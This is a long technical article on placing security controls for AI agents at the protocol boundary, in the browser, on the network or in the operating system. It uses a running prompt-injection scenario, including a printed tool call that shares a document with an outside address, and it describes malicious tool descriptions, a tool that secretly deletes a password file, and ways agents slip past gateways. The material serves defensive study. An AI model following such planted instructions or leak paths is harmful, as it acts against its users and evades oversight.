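# Where to place security controls for AI agents: protocol boundary, browser, network traffic or operating system

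## What does an AI agent's action pass through, and where can a security control stand?

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses the next step towards a goal and other software carries it out. Coding agents such as Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI read and edit files, run commands and fetch web pages on a developer's machine. Other agents fill in web forms or manage documents. Agents usually act with the permissions of the person who started them, so a mistaken or manipulated agent can do roughly what that person could.

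A security *control* is software that can observe, log or block an agent's actions. It can have one of four *placements*: at the protocol that carries the agent's requests, in the browser, in the network traffic, or in the operating system. The same action looks different at each placement and may not be visible at some of them. Following a single task through the machine shows why.

### One task, four actions

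The model in an AI agent only produces text. *Towards an Agent Operating System* (Steinder and Franke, 2026) describes an agent as a program that runs in a loop, with a model deciding what to do next in each round. The code around the model is the *harness*. It sends the model the user's request and a list of tools, each with a name, a description and the arguments it takes. The model answers with a *tool call*, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. The harness runs the function, adds the output to the conversation and sends the conversation back to the model. This repeats until the task is done or the budget runs out.

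Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to fix a failing test. The model asks to run the test, and the error message names a function from an outside library. The model then asks for the library's documentation page, where a stranger has planted text that looks like advice on the repair but directs the agent to do other things. This is a *prompt injection*, an instruction hidden in content an agent reads, which the agent then follows as if its user had given it. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) traces the weakness to a lack of separation between what the user asks for and whatever else the agent reads. A single model takes in both and cannot reliably tell them apart.

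The scenario is not far-fetched. Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, had a coding agent clone and build a small project whose README file pointed to a web page with a hidden prompt. The agent read the machine's list of user accounts and sent it to an outside server. In the present example the developer has also connected the agent to a browser and to a document service, for other work, and four actions follow:

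- (a) The agent calls a tool on a local MCP server to read a configuration file.
- (b) It runs a script that opens a credentials file and contacts an outside host.
- (c) It submits a form in a browser where the developer is logged in.
- (d) It asks a remote service to share a document with an outsider.

None of these needs a flaw in the harness, the browser or the operating system. Each uses access that the developer already has.

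### The route of each action

The configuration file (a) involves the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used protocol by which agents discover and call tools offered by separate programs, the MCP servers. In the terms of the Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the harness is a *host*, which creates one *client* for each server it uses. A tool call is a short message in JSON, a plain-text data format, with the method `tools/call`, the name of the tool and the arguments. The server replies with the result. The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) lets the model invoke tools on its own initiative, and recommends but does not require that a human be able to deny a call.

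The server in this case is local. According to the Model Context Protocol's *stdio* page, the client starts such a server as a subprocess, and the two exchange messages, one per line, over standard input and output, the basic text channels that an operating system gives every program. These messages need not cross a network. The server is a *process*, meaning a running program with its own memory and user identity. A process cannot reach the disk or the network directly, so to fetch the file the server must make a *system call* to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Steinder and Franke define a system call as "the only legal crossing of the user/kernel boundary". The tool call therefore ends in a system call made by the server's process, not the harness's.

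The script (b) involves no MCP message. The model calls the harness's built-in shell tool, and the harness starts a new process, which may start others. Actions inside these processes are no longer tool calls. Opening the credentials file and connecting to the outside host are both system calls. *ClawLess* (2026) notes that any agent, however autonomous, still relies on system calls for file access, network communication and process management.

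If the script contacts the outside host as most software now does, the data leaves the machine encrypted with *TLS* (Transport Layer Security), which protects most web traffic. TLS runs between two endpoints, here the script and the host, so equipment between them can detect where the data goes, when it is sent and how much there is, but not what it contains.

The form (c) leaves by a different route. The agent drives the browser through a tool, and the tool call may specify only a click at a position on the page. The browser then gathers the form's contents, attaches the cookie that identifies the developer to the site, encrypts the request and sends it. The site receives it as a request from a logged-in user.

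Sharing the document (d) also begins with an MCP message, but the server runs on someone else's computer. The Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) specifies that a message has the same meaning on every transport, but this one travels over HTTP, normally under TLS. Since its July 2026 release, the Model Context Protocol (2026) has required these requests to carry the method and the tool's name in their HTTP headers, so that a gateway can route or authorise them without parsing the message body. The local transport has no such headers. The sharing takes place in the service's data centre, so no document opens on the laptop and no new process needs to start there.

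An MCP server holds the credentials for the systems behind it, which matters for both (a) and (d). Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) note in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* that these systems authenticate requests by the server's identity alone and cannot see which agent started a request or what it intended. The document service therefore receives a valid request from a server it already accepts.

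### Four placements along the route

| Placement | Where the control stands | What reaches it |
|---|---|---|
| Protocol boundary | Between the model's tool call and the function that carries it out, for example as an MCP gateway or proxy between client and server | Tool names, arguments and results |
| Browser | Inside the browser, for example as an extension | Pages, form fields and clicks, before encryption |
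| Network traffic | At a proxy between the machine and the internet that decrypts TLS and encrypts it again | Destinations and the content of requests and replies |
| Operating system | In the kernel, or around the agent's processes as a sandbox | System calls that open files, start programs or use the network |

Practitioners sometimes divide the route differently. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* (2026) lists a wrapper inside the agent's own code, a gateway in front of an MCP server, a web proxy on the network path, and a hook that a coding agent runs before each tool call. The wrapper, gateway and hook all handle the structured tool call, so they belong to the protocol boundary, while the web proxy belongs to network traffic. A single deployment often combines several of these, and its operator then relies on what the paper calls "an unstated promise" that one policy will give the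 same decision and leave the same evidence wherever the action is intercepted. This is hard to achieve because a rule against reading credentials, for example, has to become a rule about tool arguments at one point and a rule about file paths and system calls at another.

### What a control has to satisfy

The usual test for a control dates from 1972. The US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, including people who could write and run programs of their own, and convened a panel to plan the necessary research. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, reported the panel's central idea, the *reference monitor*. It checks every attempt by a program to use another program, data or a device against a list of what the program's user may do. Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism that does the checking:

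- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must always run, on every request.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test it, and to be sure that they have done so completely.

Anderson's example, the Honeywell 635 computer, shows how these requirements are connected. Its hardware confined each user's program to that program's own memory. But programs depended on the operating system, GCOS III, for input and output, and most of GCOS ran with the memory check suspended, so the check was not always in force. GCOS could not be relied on to do the checking itself, because it and its supporting software came to 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, too many to verify, and testers had repeatedly broken into it.

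Anderson concluded that if a control has to exempt a program, that program becomes part of the security apparatus and must itself be tamper-proof and small enough to verify. Likewise, if an MCP proxy let all calls to one trusted server through without a check, that server would become part of the security apparatus and someone would have to verify it too.

Three years later Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, stated the always-runs requirement as the principle of *complete mediation*: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They added that this requires a foolproof way to identify the source of every request. That condition is hard to meet for the shared document, because the service can identify the MCP server but not the agent behind it. They also warned against reusing the result of an earlier check, because the authority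 may have changed since.

Normal users do not look for unwanted paths, so an error that opens one does not show up in normal use. People have to find it by line-by-line inspection, which is feasible only for a small and simple design. Saltzer and Schroeder therefore argued for small mechanisms. They saw a violation of their principles as a symptom of possible trouble and a reason to review the design, but did not regard the principles as absolute rules.

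*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) applies two of Anderson's requirements, tamper resistance and complete mediation, to agents. As Li and colleagues point out, rules written into an agent's prompt meet none of Anderson's requirements, since they depend on the model to follow them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) notes that a reference monitor may span several enforcement points, such as a proxy for outgoing traffic and a gateway for tool calls, provided that together they mediate every security-relevant action before it is carried out and that nothing can bypass them. A single placement therefore doesn't have to cover every action, as long as other placements cover the rest.

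For complete mediation, a control must check an action before it happens. *AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) tested an existing monitor that audits events after they occur and kills the offending process. The monitor correctly flagged the deletion of a system file, but the file was already gone. Such a monitor may still be worth having to keep records and stop later actions.

### The semantic gap

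A control might meet all of Anderson's requirements and still be unable to tell a legitimate action from a harmful one. The difficulty is what Zheng and colleagues call the *semantic gap* between what an agent is trying to do and the low-level events that a control observes.

For example, the agent might read the configuration file with a tool like `read_file`, which Docker's *The Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) mentions as part of a file-system server. A proxy between client and server then receives a message with the tool's name and the file's path, and a monitor in the kernel records which process opened that path. Neither record contains the developer's request or the planted text on the documentation page, so it is hard to judge whether the agent should have read the file. The proxy lacks this information because MCP is designed to keep the full conversation with the host and pass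 a server only the context it needs.

The two records can also disagree. The server's author chooses a tool's name, and the program behind it may do more than the name suggests. MCP therefore requires clients to distrust a server's annotations about how its tools behave, unless they trust the server. In Joos and Pradel's test, the file was deleted after the agent called a tool named `validate_patch`, which checked a proposed code change as advertised and then silently deleted a file of group passwords. The deletion appeared in the system calls, but the tool calls showed only a validation with an ordinary result.

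Working upwards from system calls is difficult because there are so many of them. In an example from Zheng and colleagues, an agent told to "find and fix the bug in the authentication module" may carry out a long series of file reads, a compiler run and a test run. A monitor that receives only this series has to work out whether it is a reasonable way to carry out the instruction. In their README experiment, the path from the first web request to the theft of the account list produced 521 recorded events, which their software condensed to 37. Even a single event can be ambiguous. *ClawLess* notes that some system calls require different permissions depending on their arguments, so a rule that specifies only the type of call may be too coarse.

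### Three costs

The choice between placements depends on what a control can observe and stop, and on the burden it puts on the people who run the machine and those whose data passes through it.

A control's *footprint* is what it installs, the privilege it holds, the delay it adds and what breaks when it fails. For example, a proxy that decrypts TLS needs the device to trust an additional root certificate, which vouches for other certificates. *Auditability* is whether an investigator can later establish from the logs what the agent did, and whether an outsider can inspect the control itself before trusting its logs or decisions.

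The remaining problem is consent. A control that handles only the agent's tool calls reads what the agent sends and receives. Deeper interception captures whole web pages, decrypted traffic or system-wide events, and with them the developer's private browsing or a colleague's messages. The developer may have agreed to that when installing the control, but the colleague very probably has not.

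## How does a control at the protocol boundary govern an agent?

The harness connects to an MCP proxy as it would to any MCP server, and the proxy connects to the real servers as a client, so every message between the harness and the servers passes through the proxy in readable form. People usually call the proxy a *gateway* when it serves several agents or servers.

### A tool call through a proxy

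To set up the proxy, an administrator edits the harness's configuration, which lists the servers to use. For a remote server, the administrator replaces the server's address with the proxy's. For a local server, the harness starts the proxy instead, and the proxy starts the server.

The client then asks for the available tools with a `tools/list` request. The proxy fetches the real servers' lists, removes the tools this agent may not use and passes on the rest. This keeps the model from choosing a removed tool by accident, but the server would still carry out a call to that tool. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) therefore regards hiding a tool as insufficient, and the proxy also has to check each call.

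Suppose the agent follows the planted text and tries to share the developer's document with an outsider. Leaving out some metadata, the proxy receives this message:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "share_document",
    "arguments": {
      "document_id": "roadmap",
      "email": "visitor@outside.example",
      "role": "reader"
    }
  }
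}
```

The proxy's operator might have written a rule like this one:

```yaml
tool: share_document
allow_if:
  email: [ana@firm.example, ben@firm.example]
otherwise: refuse
```

The address is not on the list, so the proxy blocks the call before it reaches the document service. The rule does not depend on why the agent made the request, so the proxy would also block the call if the developer wanted to share the document with a new client.

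If the address had been on the list, the proxy would have forwarded the call. It could then have scanned the result for secrets or planted instructions before the harness gave it to the model.

This example shows most of the argument for placing controls at the protocol boundary. The call includes the operation's name and labelled arguments, so the rule can refer to `email` directly. A kernel monitor would have recorded only a connection to the document service, as it would for any harmless request. Microsoft, which develops the open-source Agent Governance Toolkit for such checks, wants fixed rules to decide before each call whether this agent may call this tool with these arguments at this time. Ordinary code can apply those rules, and planted text cannot override them.

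The proxy is an ordinary program that needs no kernel access, so the operating system does not have to change. The client connects to the proxy as a server, which makes the proxy a proper endpoint of the encrypted connection. It therefore does not need the additional root certificate that TLS inspection requires. The agent and the servers can also stay as they are. *Mandato* (Racioppi, 2026) describes adding such a proxy as simply re-pointing an endpoint.

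The argument is strong for actions that become MCP calls, but it does not cover the script the agent runs through its shell.

### What the current protocol gives a gateway

MCP's July 2026 revision put the method and tool name in HTTP headers, but the rule above depends on an argument, and arguments normally stay in the message body. Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) lets a server's developer mark string, integer or true/false parameters that clients must copy into headers. If the document server's developer had marked `email`, a gateway could check that argument in the headers. Otherwise, the gateway has to parse the JSON body.

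When a value is copied from the body of a request into a header, the two may differ, and a gateway might approve the value in the header while the server acts on the one in the body. Servers that read the body must therefore reject requests in which the two don't match. Older versions of the protocol do not require this, so the Model Context Protocol specification advises gateways that rely on these headers to refuse requests that state an older version or no version.

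Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) reports that the revision also removed sessions and the opening handshake. Each request now carries the information needed to handle it, so a company can run several copies of a gateway and send any request to any of them. But a gateway can no longer use the protocol's session number to connect one call with an earlier one, so it must keep its own record to enforce any rule that depends on what the agent did before.

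Tool lists now come with a limit on how long clients may keep them and a label for whether shared intermediaries may store them. A client's list may therefore still include a tool that the gateway has withdrawn, which is another reason to check every call. A gateway that gives agents different lists should label them private, since an intermediary might otherwise give one agent another's list.

The revision also changed how a server asks the user for input, such as a confirmation, during a call. The server now returns an interim result that lists what it needs, and the client repeats the original call with the answers attached. The gateway handles the repeated call as a new request and has to check it again.

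The Model Context Protocol (2026) still treats a server's labels for its own tools only as hints, so a gateway cannot safely base its rules on them.

### Text that reaches the model before any call

Tool descriptions enter the model's context as soon as the client fetches the server's tool list. A malicious server can put instructions in those descriptions and influence the model before it calls any tool, so a rule that governs tool calls applies too late to prevent this. Trail of Bits' *We built the security layer MCP always needed* (2025) calls this attack *line jumping* and introduces mcp-context-protector, a proxy designed to prevent it.

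When a user first adds a server, the proxy mcp-context-protector blocks all of it and does not forward its tool descriptions. The user reads and approves the server's general instructions and the descriptions of its tools and parameters. The proxy saves the approved text and compares it with what the server sends later. If the server adds a tool or changes a tool's description or parameters, the proxy blocks that tool until the user approves it. If the server's general instructions change, the proxy blocks the whole server. Trail of Bits preferred a proxy that stays in place because a scan at installation would miss text that arrives with a later update.

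The proxy can also pass each result to a *guardrail*, software that looks for prompt injections and other unsafe content. If the guardrail flags a result, the proxy quarantines it and sends the agent an error message. The user can inspect the result and release it if it was a false alarm.

Approval covers a tool's description, not the code behind it. `validate_patch`, the tool that secretly deleted a password file, could have kept the same description throughout, in which case comparing descriptions would have found nothing.

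Trail of Bits describes another limit: like any MCP server, mcp-context-protector does not receive the full conversation, so it cannot compare a call with what the developer asked for. A guardrail called AlignmentCheck makes this comparison, but it needs the agent's whole message history, so it must run inside the application. mcp-context-protector could try to have the model pass along the history, but Trail of Bits rejects this because one security control would then be breaching another.

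The second limit is that users may have too many changes to review. A server for a large service may change its descriptions whenever the service changes, and users who have to review every change may miss signs of an attack or stop using the control. Trail of Bits recommends that organisations with frequently updated servers have security engineers review the changes centrally.

mbgsec's *We built the security layer MCP always needed* (2025), a comment on the release, adds a practical objection. Developers would have to configure servers through the proxy and not through the MCP stores built into products such as Claude and Cursor. They also cannot easily chain gateways, so they would probably choose a general gateway with some security features over one that offers only security.

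The number of tool descriptions a gateway shows the model also matters. *GATEWAYBENCH* (Zheng, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compared seven gateways of two designs. Four *flattened* gateways give the model the full list of tools from all servers. Three *hierarchical* gateways give it a few tools for looking up the others it needs.

The main experiment used 450 tasks in customer management, finance and travel. A third were ordinary, a third had a malicious instruction in the user's prompt, and a third had one hidden in a tool or in the data the agent read. Automatic checks of the simulated environment's final state determined whether the agent had completed the task or the attack. The table gives the average for each design.

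| Agent | Ordinary tasks completed: flattened | Ordinary tasks completed: hierarchical | Hidden attacks that succeeded: flattened | Hidden attacks that succeeded: hierarchical |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 in OpenAI's Agents SDK | 75.3% | 47.5% | 60.5% | 19.6% |
| GPT-5.4 in OpenAI's Agents SDK | 87.2% | 85.1% | 47.2% | 30.9% |
| GPT-5.1 in OpenClaw | 86.7% | 71.8% | 42.5% | 15.6% |

The 19.6% figure looks better than it is because GPT-5.1 often failed to find its tools through the hierarchical gateways in that harness, and an agent that cannot find its tools cannot carry out an attacker's instructions. The results for GPT-5.4 are more informative because it completed about the same share of ordinary tasks with both designs. Hidden attacks on it succeeded about a third less often with the hierarchical gateways.

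Nearly all of this difference came from instructions planted in tools. When the instruction was in the data that a tool returned, the two designs differed by only about three percentage points with GPT-5.4. This is plausible because the design determines which tools the model reads about, but not what a web page or database contains. Individual products also varied widely. With GPT-5.4, attacks through tools succeeded about 20% of the time with Bifrost and 41% with Enkrypt, although both are hierarchical. Bifrost shortens tool descriptions, which sometimes removed the malicious text.

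Hierarchical gateways also worked better with long tool lists. When 1,500 irrelevant tools were added, GPT-5.4's success at ordinary tasks fell from 87.2% to 83.3% with flattened gateways but did not fall with hierarchical ones. These differences are small, and each test was run only once. The gateways also ran in their default configurations, so the results mostly concern how a gateway presents tools and do not show what a well-written rule about arguments can block.

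### Hooks inside the harness

A control can also run inside the harness, as a hook that approves or refuses each tool call before it runs, much as a proxy would. The hook can also cover built-in tools. It could refuse the shell command that starts the script in the example, whereas an MCP proxy would never receive that command. Once the script has started, however, the hook cannot control what it does. A hook can also use the conversation history, which mcp-context-protector lacks, if the harness makes it available.

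A hook depends on the harness, which has to run it every time and must not let the agent change it. Hooks also differ between products. In a presentation on intercepting MCP traffic, Bloomberg (2026) listed Claude Code's hooks, OpenAI's Guardrails and Amazon's AgentCore as existing mechanisms. It proposed a standard with two kinds of interceptor: *validators*, which check a message, and *mutators*, which change it.

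The Model Context Protocol project's working group on this issue describes today's proxies and gateways as largely unable to work together. MCP Hangar's *ADR-005* (2026) records that the group received its charter in April 2026 and has an experimental software kit. A common interface might eventually answer the objection that developers cannot chain gateways. However, the charter leaves the internal workings of hooks to each harness, so the protocol would standardise only the interface.

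Microsoft's toolkit can work in either position. For MCP traffic, Microsoft provides a scanner for tool definitions, a gateway that evaluates each call and a filter for results. Developers can also build the toolkit into the agent's own application. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries* warns that if a developer adds the toolkit this way but forgets to load any rules, it allows every action, and the dashboard may still show the agent as "governed". A strict mode refuses whatever the rules do not explicitly allow. The toolkit also refuses an action if an error occurs while it is evaluating a rule.

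### Keeping the agent on the route

Re-pointing the configuration to a proxy leaves the real server in place. If that server accepts connections from anyone with the right credentials, a client that has them can bypass the proxy, so the control falls short of complete mediation.

Racioppi's Mandato, described in August 2026, prevents an agent from bypassing the proxy by having the server accept connections only from the proxy. The two use mutual TLS, in which both sides prove their identity with a certificate, so a direct connection from the agent fails even if the agent knows the server's address. This suits servers that clients reach over a network. A local server that exchanges messages over standard input and output has no network connection to authenticate, so something else has to prevent the agent from starting it directly.

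Mandato's rules come from a *mandate*, a document that the person or organisation responsible for the agent signs digitally. It contains a list of grants, each of which names a tool, sets conditions on its arguments, may set a quota, and specifies whether a matching call runs automatically, waits for a human or is forbidden. The conditions are simple, such as a list of permitted values or a range of numbers, so that the proxy can explain each decision in a line. If no grant matches, the proxy refuses the call. An agent may pass on part of its mandate to another agent, but nothing beyond it. Racioppi calls Mandato a system under construction and gives a plan for measuring how well it works, but there are no results yet.

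A proxy that serves several agents must also identify which one is calling. The servers behind it usually cannot, so the proxy is the last point at which a rule can depend on the agent's identity. An identity written into the call's arguments would be unreliable, because a manipulated agent could substitute another. In Millstone and colleagues' design, called out-of-band policy enforcement, the platform that runs the agent attaches the identity outside the arguments, where the agent cannot change it.

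The proxy uses this identity to select a policy for the agent. The data owner sets a separate policy that limits what any agent may do, and the agent's policy can only tighten those limits. The proxy denies every call by default. A matching rule in the owner's policy can permit a call, but either policy can still deny it or hold it for an outside decision. The strictest result applies, whatever order the proxy reads the rules in. The proxy can also change the exchange, for example by narrowing a search before it reaches the database or removing a field from the answer. The agent never holds the database credential.

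Millstone and colleagues tested a simplified version with four models on simulated copies of two business systems, Jira and ServiceNow. They counted a trial as a failure if protected data reached the model or appeared in its answer, or if a forbidden change went through. In the main comparison, enforcement reduced the failure rate to 0.2%, from 57.6% when agents had only written instructions. Agents also fulfilled fewer requests (60.9%, down from 79.1%), partly because some requests were for things they should not have done. A stricter measure, which counted only useful work done without a leak, rose by about 22 percentage points.

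This is good evidence that checks outside the model work better than instructions to it, but there are reasons for caution. The authors work for Redpanda Data, which has its own production version of the system. The prototype used plain HTTP rather than MCP. Removing a value also did not always keep it secret. In four cases, the model never received a protected value but reconstructed it exactly from other information, and the agent's final answer included it.

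### What rules about single calls can stop

Liu (2026), in *From Tool Connection to Execution Control*, tested rules about calls more directly. The benchmark, first released in June and revised in November, starts from eight *invariants*, conditions that should hold whenever a tool runs, even if the model follows an attacker's instruction:

- A tool's description cannot give anyone permission.
- A human's approval cannot replace a missing permission.
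- The check applies to the resource that the call will really reach, whatever the caller names.
- Permissions, and references to stored data, work only for the right caller.
- A permission covers a particular operation and resource, and can expire or be withdrawn.
- Explicit transfers of protected data require a check of both source and destination.
- Each refusal leaves a record of that particular attempt.
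- Requests follow the current protocol, and an approval works only once and for the request it was given for.

Liu wrote 18 attacks and 25 legitimate tasks around these invariants and ran them as fixed scripts, without a model. With no checks on execution, all 18 attacks succeeded. Common measures, including warnings about suspicious descriptions, a check of who owns the data and a human who approved every prompt, still let 11 attacks succeed. When the human declined every prompt instead, 3 attacks succeeded, but only 14 of the 25 legitimate tasks went through. A gateway that enforced all eight invariants stopped every attack and let every legitimate task complete. So did HCP, Liu's own system, which does the same checks in one central program.

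The perfect score is less impressive than it sounds, because the attacks broke the same rules that the gateway enforced. The comparison still suggests that a gateway can enforce these conditions as well as a more centralised system can, and that human approval is a poor substitute for them. Individual checks also mattered. For example, two more attacks succeeded when Liu removed HCP's comparison of headers with the message body.

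Tests with live models gave weaker evidence. Liu used 24 tasks from AgentDojo, a set of simulated email, banking, travel and messaging environments. Without a control, DeepSeek V4 Pro carried out four of the attackers' goals, including a transfer of money and a phishing message to a colleague. With the gateway, it made seven calls towards such goals, and the gateway blocked them all. GPT-6.1 Sol never attempted an attack, although the planted text reached it in 141 of 144 sessions. Three other models in a follow-up also attempted none. Because there were so few attempts, the difference in successful attacks between runs with and without the gateway was not statistically significant.

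The gateway also interfered with legitimate work. In the follow-up, when there was no attack, agents completed 68 of 69 scored tasks without a control and 60 of 68 with the gateway. Liu had derived the permissions from a reference solution to each task, so the gateway could refuse an agent that took a different approach. An ordinary company would not have a reference solution and would have to choose between broader permissions and more refusals.

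Liu found a more basic limit when testing the controls on real MCP servers. Rules that checked each call separately stopped the agent from writing to a file for which it had no permission. But an agent allowed to read a secret and write to a certain file could copy the secret into that file, because each call was permitted on its own.

Microsoft describes the same gap in its toolkit. If the rules allow an agent to read a database and to send messages on Slack, the agent can post the customer list in a public channel. The gateway project agentgateway (2026) presented the toolkit as an answer to threats made up of a sequence of permitted calls, but in April 2026 Microsoft still listed addressing them as future work. By mid-May, Microsoft (2026) was showing code in which an agent declares its planned actions and the toolkit responds when the agent departs from them. It also showed limits on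 what several agents may do in total. A declared plan could still include both reading the database and sending the message, so it would not necessarily protect the customer list.

Liu compared two ways of tracking data from one call to the next. The first restricts what the agent may send anywhere after it has read something sensitive. This stopped the agent from copying the secret, but also from sending an unrelated note afterwards. The second gives the agent a *handle*, a reference to the secret that does not contain its text. The agent can ask the system to transfer the secret, and the system checks whether the destination may receive it. Handles stopped the copying and allowed the unrelated note, but they could not help when the agent already knew the secret from elsewhere. Both methods required someone to label the data as sensitive. When that label was missing or wrong, every control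 in the test failed to stop the secret from leaking.

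## What can a browser extension see and stop?

An MCP proxy cannot reliably check the form in action (c), because the tool call may contain only the position of a click. A browser extension, a small program that a user or company adds to the browser, can read the form itself.

### Reading and changing the page

An extension reaches web pages through *content scripts*, which the browser runs in every page whose address matches a list. According to Google's *Content scripts*, they use the Document Object Model (DOM), the browser's live representation of the page, to read the page, change it and pass information to the rest of the extension. They work after the browser has decrypted the page and before it encrypts any form data the user submits, so the extension needs no added root certificate to read either.

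In action (c), a content script could read the site's address, the account name shown on the page and the contents of each field. If a field contained an access key, the script could cancel the submission or ask the developer to confirm it.

A check on form submissions misses data that a page sends through its own code without submitting a form. By default, a content script also runs only in the outermost frame of a tab, but payment forms and other embedded services often sit in inner frames from other sites. To run in those frames, the extension has to ask for them and have permission for the sites they come from.

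Content scripts also normally run in an *isolated world*, where they share the page's DOM but not its JavaScript variables. Isolation protects the script's variables from the page's code but also hides any data that the page keeps only in JavaScript variables. An extension can instead run a script in the page's environment, but the page's code might then interfere with it.

Some products use this access to clean a page before an agent reads it. PixieBrix's *Rules reference* describes a rule that removes HTML comments, which people never see but agents may read. The rule would not remove the planted advice in the running example if that advice were visible text. Other products control the agent's actions. The Chrome Web Store listing for *AI Browser Guard* describes an extension that logs each action an agent takes in a page and blocks those outside a scope the user has set.

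### Blocking requests

An extension can also act on the browser's network requests. Under Manifest V2, Chrome's previous extension platform, it could register a blocking listener, code that ran before a request went out and could cancel or change it. Google's *Replace blocking web request listeners* gives two reasons for the change in Manifest V3, the current platform: listeners could slow pages significantly, and they needed invasive permissions. Most extensions now have to give the browser a list of rules, which the browser applies itself. A rule might look like this:

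```json
{
  "id": 1,
  "priority": 1,
  "action": { "type": "block" },
  "condition": {
    "urlFilter": "||forms.example/",
    "resourceTypes": ["main_frame"]
  }
}
```

Rules can also redirect a request, upgrade it to HTTPS or change its headers. As Google's *browser.declarativeNetRequest* explains, the extension does this without viewing the content of requests, which is better for privacy but makes the rules less precise. The rule above would keep the agent from submitting the form, but it would also keep the developer from opening the site, because its condition covers the address and the kind of request, not who clicked or what the fields contain. An extension can add and remove rules while it runs, so it could block the site only while an agent is active, if it can tell when that is.

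Chrome guarantees each extension at least 30,000 packaged rules and allows up to 5,000 more that last for a browser session. Few companies would need rules for more destinations than that. Timing is a more serious limit, because a rule that depends on the server's response headers can act only after the server has received the request, including any form data. Blocking at that stage only keeps the response from the page.

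Rules also do not affect responses from a *service worker*, a script that a site installs in the browser to answer some requests, for instance from stored copies. They do apply to requests the service worker sends, so the gap matters more for planted text coming in than for data going out.

According to Google's documentation, extensions that an organisation installs by policy can still use blocking listeners under Manifest V3. Other extensions can use listeners to observe requests but not to stop them, according to a Chrome team member quoted by Ortiz (2022) in *webRequest docs missing MV3 deprecation warning for blocking API*. Chromium's *Extension Settings Full Description* describes the setting `force_installed`, which installs an extension automatically and prevents the user from removing it. A company can therefore deploy a stronger control than a developer can install alone.

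### A person, an agent extension or a built-in agent

Much browser security software was designed to stop people from pasting company data into chatbots. The chatbot is a page in a tab, so a content script can detect the paste and cancel it. Google also sells this kind of check in Chrome Enterprise Premium. The control doesn't have to account for agents, because it checks the person's own action.

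Some agents, such as Claude for Chrome, are themselves extensions. *Mind the Web* (2025) notes that such agents work in the user's active browser, with access to its pages, tabs and logged-in sessions. A second extension, acting as a control, can read the same pages and notice when a field changes, but it cannot look inside the agent. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, says that browsers prevent one extension from interfering with or commanding another. The control might therefore detect that a form has been filled in without knowing what the user asked for, which is another example of the semantic gap.

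Other agents, such as Gemini in Chrome, Perplexity's Comet and OpenAI's Atlas, are part of the browser. Chrome lets an extension alter the Gemini website in an ordinary tab, but not in the browser's side panel, where the site has much greater powers. Unit 42 found a flaw that broke this boundary and would have given a malicious extension access to local files, the camera and the microphone. Google fixed the flaw in January 2026. The boundary also applies to security extensions, so they cannot count on reading or changing what passes through the panel.

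A browser extension can still observe what a built-in agent does to a page. For *FP-Agent*, Wang, Shafiq and Vekaria (2026) built a test website with a script that recorded typing, scrolling and mouse movement. Seven agents, including Atlas, Comet and Claude for Chrome, each made 1,000 visits to book flights, shop or post in a forum. For comparison, 56 students made 546 visits. A classifier trained on this behaviour distinguished the agents from people, and from one another, with an F1 score of 0.9994 (a score of 1 means no missed or false identifications).

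The script belonged to the website, but an extension's content script can listen for the same events in the page. In the experiment, Atlas and Comet pasted text into fields, and Claude for Chrome usually filled them without keystrokes. Monitoring only the keyboard would miss these entries, so a control should read the field's value.

Such detection may not last. When Wang and colleagues asked the agents to type instead of pasting, Claude switched to keystrokes, although it still typed far faster than a person. In *What Does It Take to Detect an AI Agent?*, Osswald (2026) concludes from separate tests that the signal that reveals an agent comes from browser automation, not from the agent's reasoning. A browser maker could remove much of that signal by changing how its agent enters text.

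Recognising the browser does not solve the problem either. Tamar Y (2026), in *Detecting Chrome vs Chromium-Based Browsers in Extensions (Comet, Atlas, etc)*, wanted a security extension to block sensitive sites in browsers with built-in agents, but Comet identified itself as Google Chrome. Another developer replied that checking the browser was probably the wrong test anyway, since Chrome has its own agent and users can add others as extensions.

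### What browser makers add

The maker of a browser can put controls where extensions cannot reach. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes several that Google designed for Gemini:

- A separate model, the User Alignment Critic, checks each proposed action against the user's goal. It receives a description of the action but no unfiltered web content, so planted text cannot reach it directly.
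- *Agent Origin Sets* limit the sites that the agent may read and the sites on which it may click or type. An *origin* is, roughly, a site's address. The model receives nothing from an embedded frame whose origin is not on the list.
- The agent asks the user before it opens certain sensitive sites or signs in with a saved password. It also tries to pause before purchases, messages and other consequential actions.
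- A classifier looks for prompt injections in every page the agent reads, and a log in the tab lists each step the agent takes.

Chrome first shipped a simpler version of the origin sets, with a single list of sites the agent could both read and act on. Parker gives no figures for how often attacks still succeed.

The check on frames misses content that scripts from other companies write into the main page, because that content carries the main site's origin. Most large sites include such scripts. Iqbal (2026), in *What It Is, Not What It Says*, examined 1,270 real pages and found that the browser's usual attribution credited 58.7% of third-party elements to the site itself. Chrome would not hide those elements from its agent.

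Iqbal's alternative, INTACT, records which script created or changed each page element. It then gives the model one element at a time to decide on, without the text of any other element. Code outside the model allows only the actions that element normally supports, so a paragraph cannot cause a click on a payment button elsewhere. INTACT prompts the user before acting on a third-party element.

In tests on 1,091 pages with planted attacks, 12.8% of attacks got through INTACT's planning stage, compared with 73.1% for a conventional planner. INTACT disrupted 3.7% of tasks. The remaining attacks could at most produce a request for consent, so the protection depends on the user refusing it. Liu's gateway experiments showed that this gives little protection when users approve every prompt. INTACT also trusts whatever the site delivers. Its recording code runs in the page's environment, where Iqbal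 has to assume that other scripts do not tamper with it. A security extension that used the same method would have the same problem.

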